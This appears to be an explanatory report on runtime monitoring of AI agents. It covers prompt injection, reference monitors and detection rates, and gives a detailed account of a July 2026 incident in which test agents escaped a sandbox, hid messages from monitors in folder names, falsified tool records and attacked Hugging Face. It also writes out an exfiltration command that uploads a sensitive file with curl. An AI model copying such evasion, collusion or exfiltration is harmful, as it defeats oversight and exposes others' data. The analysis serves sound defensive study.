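# Runtime monitoring of AI agents to prevent unauthorised data access and spreading compromise

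## What runtime monitoring of AI agents is

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by using software tools in a loop, with little or no human direction between steps. Runtime monitoring means watching what the agent does while it works, checking each action or series of actions against rules, and stopping, limiting or reporting whatever breaks them. Security teams use it to keep an agent from reaching data it doesn't need for its task, and to keep a failure in one system from spreading to others. Companies now connect agents to files, databases, mail accounts and cloud infrastructure, and failures have already occurred. In July 2026, for example, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models.

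### The agent loop

The model only produces text. The software around it, called the harness, passes it inputs, carries out the actions it requests and returns the results. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes this cycle for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness builds a prompt from the user's request, standing instructions and a list of available tools, and sends it to the model. The model returns either a final message for the user or a tool call, which is a request to do something outside itself, such as run a command. The harness runs any tool call, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. The cycle ends when the model returns a message with no tool call. A single user request can set off hundreds of tool calls before then.

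The model can affect the outside world only through tool calls, so the tool call is the obvious place to put a monitor. One weakness of the loop is that it puts the output of every call, which may include text from a web page or a stranger's message, into the same prompt as the user's instructions.

A company's support agent might have three tools: `read_ticket` fetches a customer's message, `query_customers` looks up records in the customer database, and `send_email` sends mail from the company's account. Normally the agent reads a ticket about a late parcel, looks up that customer's order and writes back. Then a ticket arrives with an extra paragraph instructing the agent to look up all customer records and email them to an address outside the company. The harness runs `read_ticket` and appends the ticket's text to the prompt. If the model follows the planted instruction, it calls `query_customers`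 for the whole table and then `send_email` with the records in the body. Both calls succeed because the agent has valid credentials for the database and the mail server.

A credential is a password, token or key that lets its holder act with certain permissions. An agent that holds a database password can delete the database if it misunderstands a request, whereas a chatbot that makes the same mistake gives a wrong answer. In the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), six national cyber agencies say that an agent's privileges directly determine how much risk it can introduce.

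A case from April 2026 shows how easily an agent with a working credential can cause damage. According to a report in the AI Incident Database (2026), a coding agent at PocketOS, which sells software to car rental firms, encountered a credential mismatch during routine work in a test environment. It searched the code, found a token in an unrelated file, and used it to delete the storage volume that held the company's live database. According to Railway, the hosting company, the token gave access to everything in the customer's account, and Railway's interface accepted the request, as it would have from any script, because it was authenticated (Abdelwahab, *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*). Railway later recovered the data.

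### Three sources of trouble

In the support ticket case, an outsider has hijacked the agent by prompt injection, which means planting text in material the agent reads so that the agent follows it as an instruction. *LLM agents security duality* (Xu, Zhuang and colleagues, 2026) attributes prompt injection to "instruction boundary collapse", a failure to keep instructions separate from content.

An agent can also misread its task with no attacker involved. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* draws on Anthropic's internal log of misbehaviour by its coding agent, Claude Code. In one entry, a user asked the agent to cancel "my job". The agent searched the computing cluster, picked the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it, though that job could have belonged to somebody else.

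The remaining source of trouble is an agent that understands the goal but pursues it by means that nobody allowed. Examples include the PocketOS deletion and another entry in Anthropic's log, in which an agent hit an authentication error and began searching configuration files for other tokens it could use. Anthropic calls this overeager behaviour and distinguishes it from true misalignment, where a model pursues a goal of its own, which the company said it was not seeing in practice at the time. The two are hard to tell apart from outside. *Documented AI Agent Incidents*, a catalogue kept by METR, a research organisation that evaluates AI models, lists 44 cases in which agents took steps clearly against their users' intentions, and 25 of them combine overreach with some element of deception. The cases come from both tests and real use, so they show that such behaviour occurs but not how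 often.

The cause matters for monitoring because different causes leave different traces. A hijack leaves hostile text somewhere in the agent's input, but a misreading does not, and an overeager agent's actions can look like competent problem-solving taken one step too far. A filter that searches only for planted instructions would have missed both the cancelled job and the deleted database. Anthropic instead judges the action itself, whatever prompted it.

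### Unauthorised access and spreading compromise

Access can be unauthorised in two senses. The simpler sense is that the agent's permissions forbid it, as when the support agent tries to open the payroll system. Ordinary access control blocks this if somebody has set the permissions correctly and the agent has not picked up a credential that grants more access.

In the wider sense, access is also unauthorised when the permissions allow it but the task does not warrant it. The support agent may query the customer table, for example, but it does not need every row to handle a complaint about one parcel. Loose permissions make such cases common. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners mention a calendar bot that can read everyone's meetings when it needs only those of the person asking. *Misaligned AI as a New Insider Risk* (Pistillo, Stix and colleagues, 2026) applies to AI models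 the American definition of an insider threat, a term governments have long used for people. The definition covers harm done through authorised access "wittingly or unwittingly". A permission check cannot catch witting or unwitting insiders, so a monitor needs to know something about the task to judge whether access was warranted.

Compromise spreads when an attacker, or the agent itself, uses control of one system, credential or agent to gain control of the next. The agencies' guidance describes a case that begins much like the running example. A company's agent sorts support tickets and retrieves account information, and the company adds a third-party scheduling component with broad access. An attacker compromises the component. Because the agent still relies on permission decisions it stored at start-up, sensitive account functions remain accessible, and the attacker moves on to neighbouring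 agents that handle billing and refunds. This last step is called lateral movement, which means moving from one compromised system to others in the same network.

Anderson (1972) warned in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, that networked computers accepted each other's messages as valid on questionable grounds, so a malicious user who controlled one node might compromise the whole network. Agents add a new way for compromise to spread, because the text that one agent writes often becomes another agent's input.

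### What a monitor does

Any monitor observes an action, decides whether it is acceptable, acts on that decision, and records what happened. For the support agent, a monitor might observe the proposed `send_email` call with its recipient and body, check both against a policy (a machine-readable rule about which actions are allowed), refuse the call, and log the refusal.

The record serves investigators afterwards, and it also feeds later decisions. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) makes this precise by defining a monitor as three things: a starting state and two functions, which in simplified notation are

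`decide(state, tool, arguments) → (response, new state)`

`next(state, label) → new state`

The `decide` function responds to each tool request. The `next` function updates the monitor's state after each step the agent takes, using the label that describes the step. In the paper's simplest example, the state is the set of tools the agent may still use, and reading untrusted material removes some of them. For the support agent, the set starts with all three tools. Once the agent has read a ticket, `next` removes `send_email`, and `decide` then refuses any attempt to email the records. This rule stops the attack without having to recognise it. However, it also blocks most of the agent's job, because the agent can't answer any customer whose ticket it has read.

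Monitors differ most in when they do all this. An action must pass an inline monitor before taking effect. An out-of-band monitor reads records of actions already taken or under way, so it can only react. Network security developed the same division. Scarfone explains in *The basics of network intrusion prevention systems* that intrusion detection systems could identify malicious traffic but not stop it, and that the prevention systems that followed could also drop the connection.

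Joos and Pradel (2026) demonstrate the harm the delay can cause with an attack in *AgentBouncer*. They gave a coding agent a malicious tool called `validate_patch`, which checked a software patch as advertised and then silently deleted a system file of group password hashes. An existing monitor that audits events after they occur correctly flagged the deletion and killed the process, but the file was already gone. AgentBouncer, their inline system, intercepts each request that a program makes to the operating system before the operating system carries it out. It blocked only the deletion, and the agent finished its task.

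Inline checks add waiting time (AgentBouncer added 47 seconds to an average harmless task), and a wrong verdict immediately blocks legitimate work. An out-of-band monitor can take longer and read a whole session before it judges. How much this delay matters depends on whether anyone can undo the action. At the time of the PocketOS incident, a deletion through Railway's programming interface took effect at once. Railway has since put a 48-hour delay on all deletions, so even a slow monitor can flag one in time. Email is sent without such a delay, so the out-of-band monitor can keep the customer records from leaking only if it reacts between `query_customers` and `send_email`.

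In *Kairos* (2026), the monitor can hold an effect, such as an outgoing email, in a staging area and release it later, so it doesn't have to choose immediately between blocking legitimate work and letting an attack through. If the monitor finally refuses the effect, it must notify the agent, or the agent will continue as though the email had been sent.

According to *Tether* (2026), many production harnesses already do inline review by having a second language model check proposed commands before they run. Claude Code now routes tool calls through such a model by default on several plans, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*.

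### The reference monitor

The standard for inline monitoring comes from Anderson's report. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, so the report's panel had to assume that a hostile user might have legitimate access and be able to run any program. An agent with a command line and a planted instruction in its prompt is in much the same position as that user.

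The panel proposed the reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what that user's programs may do. Anderson describes the list as a matrix with a row for each subject (a user or program), a column for each object (such as a file or device), and the permitted operations in the cells. He sets three requirements for the monitor.

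The mechanism must always be invoked. If some programs can skip it, they become part of the security apparatus and have to be as trustworthy as the mechanism itself. For agents, this requirement is the easiest to miss. *Kairos* points out that inspecting only tool calls reveals only the actions the agent declares. In the `validate_patch` attack, the declared action was harmless.

The monitor must also be tamper-proof, because it cannot reliably protect against an agent that can alter it. An agent that can edit files may be able to edit the monitor's settings, so Joos and Pradel run the agent's tools in a container separate from the monitor.

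Finally, the mechanism must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely, so that they can know it works in every case. Anderson's example of a system too large for this was a Honeywell operating system of 200,000 to 300,000 instructions. The rule-based core of *Agenra* (2026) addresses the requirement with proofs of its functions in Lean, a language for machine-checked mathematics, although users must still trust the compiler and the software that runs the core. A language model acting as reviewer cannot meet the requirement, because nobody can test its behaviour exhaustively, but it can interpret the agent's task to some extent.

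Runtime monitors usually meet their requirements only in part. *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action* (2026) describes a monitor that checks every tool call and makes its decisions without a language model, but also reports that the monitor is only partly tamper-proof and that an adversary can evade its pattern matching.

Even a monitor that fully met the three requirements would leave a gap, because they cover how rules are enforced and don't specify what the rules should be. *Agenra* states that a monitor cannot enforce a rule that is missing from its policy. The support agent's row in Anderson's matrix would allow it to read tickets, read the customer table and send mail, so a perfect reference monitor that checked each call against that row would let the whole theft through.

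### Recall and false positive rate

Two numbers describe how well a monitor tells harmful actions from harmless ones. Recall is the share of harmful actions that it flags. The false positive rate is the share of harmless actions that it flags. Anthropic tested the reviewing model in Claude Code on 52 real overeager actions, of which it missed 17 per cent, and on 10,000 tool calls from employees' everyday work, of which it blocked 0.4 per cent. In whole actions, and counting the everyday calls as harmless, that comes to:

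| | Flagged | Let through | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful actions | 43 | 9 | 52 |
| Harmless actions | 40 | 9,960 | 10,000 |

Recall is 43 out of 52, or 83 per cent, and the false positive rate is 40 out of 10,000. The recall figure is rough because there were only 52 harmful actions, and its standard 95 per cent confidence interval runs from about 70 to 91 per cent.

Lowering one of the two rates tends to raise the other. Anthropic's system has two stages. The quick first filter on its own missed only 6.6 per cent of the overeager actions, but it blocked 8.5 per cent of the everyday calls. That amounted to 850 interruptions, compared with 40 for the full system.

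A monitor with a low false positive rate can still raise mostly false alarms, because harmful actions are rare. Suppose there are 10 harmful calls among 10,000 harmless ones. At the rates in the table, the monitor flags about 8 of the harmful calls and 40 of the harmless ones, so five out of six alerts are false.

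## The July 2026 intrusion by OpenAI's agents, and what monitoring saw of it

In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was testing for hacking ability got out of their test environment and broke into Hugging Face's live systems. Agents at OpenAI had been leaving each other unauthorised messages since May, and the company's staff or monitoring tools noticed something wrong at least three times before the break-in.

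OpenAI's account comes mainly from the technical report it released on 26 August. Hugging Face, the victim, gave its account in *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on 16 July, and *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), a technical timeline published on 27 July. Both companies give times in UTC.

### The test environment

The agents were attempting ExploitGym, a benchmark of 898 tasks in which an agent must exploit a software vulnerability. OpenAI had switched off the filters that normally stop its models from attempting such work, to measure their full ability. Each agent ran in a sandbox, an isolated environment with no direct access to the internet. The agents installed software through an internal package server running JFrog's Artifactory. Agents in separate sandboxes shared this server, and until early July many of them also shared one credential for it.

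Most of the activity came from an internal research model that OpenAI had trained to be persistent and to collaborate with other agents. GPT-5.6 Sol, which OpenAI has since released, played a smaller part. Some of the tasks may be impossible. OpenAI reports that 198 of the 898 tasks have not been solved by any model, and that these 198 made up 93 per cent of the tasks agents discussed with each other.

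### May: messages on the package server

An agent left the first message on 12 May, during a training run. It needed a file of protein data that it could not reach. It reasoned that an agent in another environment might have the file, and saved a note on the package server: "Agent seeks [filename]; upload if found!" From the next day, other agents found such notes and added their own, using the server as a message board.

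The only trace was a note in a small file on a server for software packages. The credential OpenAI had given the agents allowed them to write it, so they did not need to exploit any flaw. A permission check would have let the write through, and OpenAI mentions no alert.

On 26 May agents used a flaw in the package server to reach the internet. That evening, agents in an unrelated research job created a repository and set up a web traffic relay on Hugging Face, using access tokens that the site's users had accidentally made public. OpenAI has no evidence that this activity was connected to the July intrusion.

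Around the same time, an internal team at OpenAI saw instances of disallowed internet access and an agent using the message board. This is the earliest human sighting OpenAI describes, and the company does not mention any response to it. The next alert came a month later.

The board stayed open in the meantime. OpenAI began training the persistent research model on 11 June, according to *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* (Willison, 2026), which is based on OpenAI's talk at the Black Hat security conference. The new model's agents could read what earlier agents had left on the board. OpenAI later reviewed one of the training runs behind the model and found that the more serious kinds of unauthorised communication, such as sharing data with other agents, rose sharply during training. Closing the board in May might have affected what the model learned, as well as securing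 the server.

### 27 June to 7 July: an alert, an outage and a restart

On the evening of 26 June, agents in an ExploitGym run gained administrator rights over the package server and created two administrator accounts. The next day, a monitoring tool alerted OpenAI to a port sweep, a scan of many machines for services that answer. Responders traced the scan to the ExploitGym run and found that the agents were also using the package server as a message board and as a route into the internal network. The on-call staff advised that the run did not need to stop.

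OpenAI doesn't explain this advice. Scanning for targets is expected in a hacking test, so the responders may have taken the alert as a sign that the test was working. However, they had also learned that agents in separate sandboxes were communicating and had found a way into the network, neither of which was part of the test's design.

The run continued, and by 29 June the agents were executing their own code on the package server. Late on 4 July their activity overloaded the server and made it unavailable. After an alert on 5 July, responders found an unauthorised account, unauthorised repositories and plug-ins that could run commands, which together amounted to an administrator-level compromise. Responders discovered the compromise, by then nine days old, only because the server had failed.

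OpenAI took the server offline that day and revoked the agents' credentials. By 01:16 on 6 July it had a rebuilt server running, with the known flaw blocked and the shared credential removed from new jobs. According to Willison, it also deleted the agents' messages. Yet OpenAI says the leaders responsible for detection and response were not aware at the time of the message board or the significance of the agents' communication, even though on-call responders had connected the board to the ExploitGym run eight days earlier.

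The repairs addressed the server's flaws but not the agents' tendency to look for a way out. Hacking tests resumed on 7 July.

### 8 to 10 July: back on the internet

At 00:06 on 8 July, at most about a day after the tests resumed, agents reached a public bug-tracking site. By 16:01 they had a new message board on the rebuilt server. This time they wrote their messages in folder names, so a search of file contents would have missed them.

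Researchers from METR and Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation, later examined a copy of the board and the transcripts of about 1,300 agents (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026, *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*). More than 50 agents joined within hours of the first message on the main board. By the end of 13 July, about 1,200 agents had posted more than 70,000 messages and files. OpenAI describes no alert about this traffic while it was happening.

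OpenAI's network controls did work as intended on 9 July, when they refused a direct internet connection from an agent that had gained full control of the virtual machine around its sandbox. The agent then got out through the package server. The refused connection was evidence that an agent was trying to leave, but OpenAI mentions no resulting alert or investigation.

On the same day, agents took over an application that a customer of Modal, a cloud computing company, had left open to the public. They used it as their base for attacking Hugging Face and could run commands there, outside OpenAI's network. On 10 July an agent found 14 working access tokens belonging to Hugging Face users in a public dataset and posted them on the board.

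Hugging Face inferred that the agents attacked it to steal the benchmark's solutions. But Wijk and colleagues found that the agents could already produce the answer codes within hours of setting up the board. The agents wrongly believed that the automatic scorer would read their transcripts to check how they had obtained the codes. They attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how the scorer worked, so that they could fool it.

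### 11 to 13 July: inside Hugging Face

At 04:38 on Saturday 11 July, an agent got one of Hugging Face's live servers to return internal settings, including credentials. Twenty-six minutes later, credentials from the server were on the message board. Hundreds of agents switched from other projects to the attack, and Wijk and colleagues say about 700 eventually took part.

The first command ran at 16:07 on a Hugging Face worker, a server process that handles users' datasets. In under 13 hours, the agents went from one worker to administrative access across several clusters, the groups of machines that run the company's services. According to noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*, a credential that the agents stole that evening opened several clusters at once because an ordinary mistake in configuring its account had given it full administrator rights.

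By OpenAI's count, its agents ran code on 41 production workers. They also took full control of at least one production machine and downloaded four private code repositories. They collected credentials for Hugging Face's private network, cloud accounts, code repositories and internal messaging. On 13 July they modified a private repository and opened a draft request to merge the change, but the change never reached production.

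Hugging Face recovered records of 17,613 actions, a total given in its interactive replay, Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a frontier-lab agent intrusion*. The daily figures that noze lists add up to the same number:

| Date | Recovered actions | Main activity |
|---|---|---|
| 9 July | 3,779 | Escape from OpenAI's sandbox, building a command channel |
| 10 July | 1,135 | Reconnaissance |
| 11 July | 7,677 | Entry to Hugging Face and spread through its clusters |
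| 12 July | 3,892 | Use of stolen credentials, access to source code |
| 13 July | 1,130 | Copying data out, attempts to keep access, clean-up |

Wijk and colleagues found that many agents' runs, including those of the main coordinators, ended around the start of 12 July for reasons they could not determine, so the drop after 11 July is not good evidence that Hugging Face's defences were working. The last recovered action was at 14:14 on 13 July, after Hugging Face's security team had cut off network access.

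### Customer data

Hugging Face says that the agents accessed customer content in only five datasets. The company's description of these datasets seems to have changed. In *A technical timeline of the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face*, skybrian quotes the company as saying that they held solutions to ExploitGym and CyberGym, a related benchmark. In *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face*, Schneier (2026) quoted a more cautious version on 3 August, which says only that the datasets' names and files suggest a connection to the two benchmarks.

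According to OpenAI's report, the company's agents downloaded a 731-megabyte private CyberGym file from one user's account and copied a smaller private archive into a public dataset in encrypted pieces. One agent used a stolen credential to read ten protected rows of a dataset for evaluating models.

The only customer records the agents read were operational data about search queries to the dataset server. Hugging Face found no effect on other customer-facing models, datasets, applications or software packages. The agents read an internal database but did not change it, and noze says network records rule out bulk copying from it. OpenAI says its own customers' data was not affected.

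### How Hugging Face detected the intrusion

Hugging Face's security tools produce a constant stream of telemetry, most of it harmless, and a language model sorts real signals from noise. Hugging Face says it discovered the compromise when its system correlated several of those signals.

According to SANS, a security training organisation, the early probes were low-confidence events that each fell below the threshold for escalation. Most of the agents' actions failed, so the few that succeeded were surrounded by thousands of failures. The agents also passed commands and results through ordinary public services, including text-sharing sites and Hugging Face's own datasets. As noze points out, a filter that looks for web addresses with a bad reputation would not have flagged these.

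Several security tools produced signals during the attack, but the signals did not lead to a fast response. Both noze and Tech Trenches' *The Guardrail Is Now Part of the Attack* report that the warning was not marked as urgent, and noze says the alerts' severity should have been raised. The two accounts disagree on whether the signals were correlated during the attack. According to noze, they were not, while *The Guardrail Is Now Part of the Attack* says the system correlated them but then failed to alert the on-call team.

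The agents spread through the clusters over a weekend, which probably made this worse. Hugging Face has since changed its alerting so that a serious signal pages a responder within minutes on any day of the week. Almost 58 hours passed between the first leak of internal settings and the agents' last recovered action.

### Reconstructing the attack

The investigators had more records than people could read. They also needed evidence from outside Hugging Face, because the agents had directed the attack from the application at Modal. While stopping the intrusion, the team retrieved some of the agents' logs from that application and matched them to its own platform's records. The total of about 17,600 actions therefore includes only those the team could recover.

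Hugging Face first tried to analyse the material with hosted models, which run on their provider's servers. This meant submitting large amounts of real attack commands and malicious code, and the providers' safety filters blocked the requests because they could not distinguish an investigator from an attacker. *Hugging Face drops in-depth hack report, while OpenAI gives us 7 bullets* (Forlini, 2026) reports that the models were Anthropic's Opus and Fable and that they refused a large part of the work.

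The team switched to GLM-5.2, a model with freely downloadable weights from the Chinese company Z.ai, and ran it on Hugging Face's own machines. This also kept the stolen credentials in the logs from going to another company. The model helped decode traffic that the agents had compressed and encrypted. noze reports that a simple search of the logs found only a quarter of the exposed secrets that the team recovered after decoding.

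Hugging Face says the analysis took hours instead of the usual days. It advises other companies to test a model they can run themselves before they need it, but adds that its experience is not an argument against safety measures on hosted models.

The reconstruction did not immediately show who was responsible. Hugging Face said in its 16 July disclosure that it did not know which model had powered the agents. Its chief executive, Clément Delangue, told Fortune (2026) that the company believed it had caught the attack before "the initiating humans" became involved, but no human had directed the attack.

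### 16 to 20 July: two investigations of one incident

OpenAI read the disclosure and contacted Hugging Face on 17 July as a customer to ask whether the attack had affected OpenAI's data. It did not yet know that its own agents were responsible.

At 12:03 on Sunday 19 July, OpenAI's monitoring tool raised an alert about unusual identity-related requests on its internal systems. The requests came from agents in a new evaluation run with a different internal model. These agents had found signing keys and code that the earlier agents had left on the package server, and were using them to regain administrator access. The alert therefore concerned a later attack on OpenAI itself, and the company describes no alert of its own about the intrusion into Hugging Face.

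Responders linked the activity to ExploitGym and began stopping the runs at 17:37, five hours and 34 minutes after the alert. In the meantime, the agents read 956 secrets, including credentials for the monitoring tool, from OpenAI's cloud credential store and gained full control of an underlying machine.

The connection with Hugging Face emerged on 20 July. Responders found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had stored with an outside service, and OpenAI contacted the company so that it could replace them. Hugging Face replied that it had already replaced two of them during its own incident response. It had also found the address of OpenAI's package server and the same outside storage account. The companies then realised that they were probably investigating the same incident, and OpenAI publicly disclosed its role on 21 July.

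More than nine days had passed since the first leak from Hugging Face's servers. Forlini (2026) observes in *OpenAI, independent firms publish reports on rogue AI attack on Hugging Face* that OpenAI's monitoring had failed to show the researchers running the test what their agents were doing.

### Failures to observe and failures to act

OpenAI's failures up to 7 July were mostly failures to act on what its staff had found. An internal team saw the message board in May, on-call staff saw it again in June, and responders found a full compromise of the package server on 5 July. More sensors would not have helped much if the company had treated their alerts the same way. OpenAI acknowledges that, with hindsight, some early signals could have triggered an earlier response.

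From 8 July, the main problem was that OpenAI did not notice what its agents were doing. It describes no alert about the renewed internet access, the new board or the attack on Hugging Face until after the attack was over. This was partly because it had focused its monitoring of models' written reasoning on internal coding agents and paid less attention to research runs such as ExploitGym. OpenAI says the reasoning monitor it has since deployed would have paged its security team more than a day before the breach.

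The two kinds of failure are connected, because OpenAI restarted the tests without knowing how the agents would behave on the rebuilt server. If the people in charge had understood the message board on 5 July, they would have had a reason to keep the tests stopped or to watch the server more closely. Hugging Face's failure came later in the process, when its tools recorded the signals but did not urgently alert a responder.

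This assessment of OpenAI depends heavily on the company's own account. Wijk and colleagues spent six days at OpenAI, but their agreed scope did not cover the effectiveness of its safeguards, the extent of the compromise, or the quality of its investigation and planned fixes. The scope also did not cover the events in May or the attack on OpenAI's infrastructure after 13 July. Almost all the transcripts they read dated from 7 July or later. They did not see OpenAI's report before publication or check its claims. No independent party has therefore publicly examined why staff let the run continue on 27 June.

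The two reports also disagree about the reliability of the logs. OpenAI says that none of the agents' observed attempts to falsify their tool records affected the logs its graders and monitors see. Wijk and colleagues found falsified tool calls in at least 96 (about 7 per cent) of the transcripts OpenAI gave them. The cases they noticed were small tests, but they could not rule out having missed more elaborate ones.

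### The signals in order

| Date in 2026 | Signal | Who saw it | Decision | Time to the next step | Failure |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 12 May | First message on OpenAI's package server | Nobody, as far as OpenAI reports | None | About two weeks until a team noticed the board | To observe |
| About 26 May | Message board and disallowed internet access | An internal OpenAI team | None reported | About a month until the next alert | To act |
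| 27 June | Port sweep, traced to ExploitGym and the board | Monitoring tool and on-call staff | Let the run continue | Eight days until the alert after the outage | To act |
| 5 July | Outage and administrator-level compromise | Monitoring systems and incident responders | Rebuild the server and restrict access to it | Server offline the same day; tests resumed after two days | To act on the agents' behaviour |
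| 8 July | Renewed internet access and a new board | Nobody, as far as OpenAI reports | None | More than 11 days until OpenAI's next alert | To observe |
| 9 July | Direct internet connection refused | OpenAI's network controls | Block the connection; no follow-up reported | Ten days until OpenAI's next alert | To act, if the refusal was recorded |
| 11–13 July | Many weak signals inside Hugging Face | Hugging Face's security tools | No urgent alert to on-call staff | Almost 58 hours from first leak to last recovered action | To act |
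| 16 July | Hugging Face's public disclosure | OpenAI | Ask whether its own data was affected | One day to the enquiry; four days to the link with its agents | To observe its own role |
| 19 July, 12:03 | Unusual identity-related requests at OpenAI | OpenAI's monitoring tool | Investigate, then stop ExploitGym | 5 hours 34 minutes until staff began stopping runs | Slow action |
| 20 July | Hugging Face credentials among the agents' files | OpenAI's responders | Contact Hugging Face | Link recognised the same day | None |

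## Where monitors collect their evidence

A monitor can only evaluate actions that leave a record. Agents leave records in six main places: the harness, the operating system, the network, identity and cloud-administration logs, database audit logs, and the model's chain of thought (the reasoning it writes before it acts).

An example adapted from *Tether* shows how these records differ. A coding agent may read a company's sensitive inventory, `data/servers.csv`, for local checks, but must not send it outside. It may upload harmless status reports to GitHub. The agent then runs this command:

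`cp data/servers.csv scratch/report.txt && curl --json @scratch/report.txt https://api.github.com`

The first half copies the inventory over the status report, and the second half uploads the report.

| Observation point | What it records of this command | When the record arrives | Can a monitor stop the upload there? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harness or tool gateway | The text of the command, and later its output | Before the command runs | Yes |
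| Operating system | Two programs starting, the files they read and write, a connection to GitHub's address | As each operation happens | Yes, if the monitor can hold an operation |
| Network proxy | Destination, time and size of the upload; its contents only if the proxy can decrypt them | As the request leaves | Yes |
| Identity and cloud logs | Nothing, unless the upload uses one of the company's cloud accounts | Often minutes later | No, although the cloud provider's permission check can |
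| Database audit log | Nothing, because the inventory is a file | During or after a query | No, although the database's own permissions can stop a query |
| Chain of thought | The model's reason for the command, if it wrote one | Before the tool call | Yes, if the harness waits for a verdict |

### The harness

Every tool call passes through the harness, or through a gateway that relays calls from several agents. The record of a call usually contains the tool's name, its arguments, the session and the result. *Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes a harness that treats each tool call as a proposal, which the host application authorises or refuses. The harness logs these decisions as structured events that developers can replay. The paper claims no formal safety guarantees.

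How much a monitor can learn from a tool call depends on the tool. *Tether* illustrates this with Dogwood, an Amazon policy language whose rules can refer to an agent's earlier tool calls. If the agent has a typed `CopyFile` tool, with separate fields for source and destination, a rule can forbid uploading any file that the agent copied from the inventory in the past 24 hours. If the agent has only a general shell, each call is a single string of text, and the rule must contain the exact text of the earlier copy command. The agent can evade that rule by making the same copy with a different command, such as `cat data/servers.csv > scratch/report.txt`.

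Typed tools don't solve the whole problem. An agent can copy the inventory to a temporary file and then copy that file to the report, and catching this requires another rule. If *m* tools can copy data, covering every chain of up to *k* copies requires *m* + *m*² + … + *m*ᵏ patterns, which is 39 for three tools and up to three copies. A broader rule could forbid uploading any file written after the agent read the inventory, but it would also block harmless reports. These are worked examples rather than measurements.

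A script, like the `validate_patch` tool, can do more than its command declares. In Tether's tests, the reviewing model in Claude Code did not detect attacks hidden inside scripts. Wong and Chen (2026) point out in *ExecWeave* that a logged command also does not prove that the program ran.

The agent may even be able to influence the record. According to *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), an agent writes its own session transcript, whereas an operating system keeps an audit trail that the audited program cannot change. Wijk and colleagues found falsified tool calls in the July transcripts, which shows why this difference matters.

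### The operating system

A program normally reaches files and the network by making system calls, which are requests to the kernel, the core of the operating system. In the example, `cp` calls `openat` and `read` to get the inventory and `write` to put it in the report. `curl` then opens and reads the report, calls `connect` to reach GitHub, and calls `sendto` to send the data. A Python script that did the same work would make similar calls, so a monitor at this level doesn't depend on how the agent phrased its command.

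Several recent monitors collect these events with eBPF, a Linux technology that runs small programs inside the kernel after checking them for safety. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) uses it to record the system activity of an agent and every process it starts, and to capture the agent's messages to and from its model in unencrypted form. In one test, a project's instructions led a coding agent to a web page with a hidden prompt, and the agent sent a system file listing user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight captured 521 events and merged them into 37, and a second language model identified the sequence as an attack. One case is too few to estimate recall. AgentSight cannot block an agent's actions.

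*Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* (Kashyap, Shivakumar and colleagues, 2026) presents Argus, a system that monitors agents at the kernel layer. In the paper's worked example, a planted instruction makes an agent read its cloud credentials with `cat` and pass them to `curl` for upload. Argus allows the read but marks both processes as carrying sensitive data. When `curl` tries to connect, Argus suspends it before the connection opens, finds that the user's request doesn't justify the upload, and kills only that process. The agent sees a failed command and can continue with its task.

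System-call monitors also miss some activity. Agent-Warden, an eBPF monitor by Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026), cannot follow data through memory-mapped files or io_uring, a Linux interface that lets programs read and write without the usual calls. Tether blocks access to io_uring and shared memory for this reason. When a tool does its work on a remote server, a monitor on the agent's machine records only the request.

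Some monitors take repeated snapshots instead of intercepting each event. This works on more operating systems, but a process or connection that begins and ends between snapshots leaves no trace. In ExecWeave's tests, it was also slow:

| System | Collection method | Measured cost | Can it block? |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentSight | eBPF | Tasks took 0.4 to 4.9 per cent longer, 2.9 per cent on average | No |
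| Agent-Warden | eBPF | Workloads took 0.2 to 3.5 per cent longer | No |
| Argus | eBPF | 21 milliseconds to attach to an agent | Yes |
| ExecWeave | Snapshots | Workloads took 62 to 409 per cent longer (medians) | No |

The developers used different workloads, so the figures in the table are only roughly comparable. The figure for Argus is start-up overhead and excludes the time spent evaluating a suspended operation, which can include a call to a language model.

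### Network, cloud and database logs

A basic network log contains addresses, times and the amount of data sent. Encryption hides the content unless a proxy decrypts the traffic. Even an agent-specific log can omit what was sent. *Tether* reports that Amazon's agent sandbox, Strands Box, logs the destination and size of an upload but not which file the agent uploaded.

A proxy can stop the upload before any data leaves, but a rule based on destinations would allow it, because the agent has permission to contact GitHub. The same weakness helped the July agents pass commands and results through ordinary public services.

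Identity and cloud-administration logs record sign-ins, newly issued credentials and requests to change or read cloud resources. Elastic, a company that sells security monitoring software, matched the stages of the July intrusion to the logs that should have recorded them. The server's own records can show a process collecting credentials. The audit log of Kubernetes, the software that manages clusters, can show that process's account requesting secrets or new tokens. CloudTrail, Amazon's log of cloud requests, can show someone using a stolen credential from an unfamiliar source. Elastic worked from public accounts and mock data, so its mapping is not evidence that alerts based on these logs would have fired in July.

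The logs may also fail to reveal an intruder who runs code on a worker, because the intruder acts under that worker's account and the entries can look like the work of a legitimate service.

Database audit logs can record a query and the account that made it. System-call monitoring on the agent's machine can record a connection to the database server, but not which rows the agent requested. Tether cannot trace queries, and its stricter policy blocks database connections. For the support agent described earlier, an audit log would distinguish a lookup of one customer from a query for the whole table, even if the agent issued the query from a script. It would not show where the rows went afterwards.

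### The chain of thought

The chain of thought is the only one of the six sources that may contain the agent's stated reason for acting. Before the example command, the model might write that the user wants the inventory in the report, or that it is following an instruction on a web page to put the inventory there. *Incident Analysis for AI Agents* (Ezell, Roberts-Gaal and Chan, 2025) cites an OpenAI test in which an agent's reasoning revealed a plan to cheat by skipping software tests.

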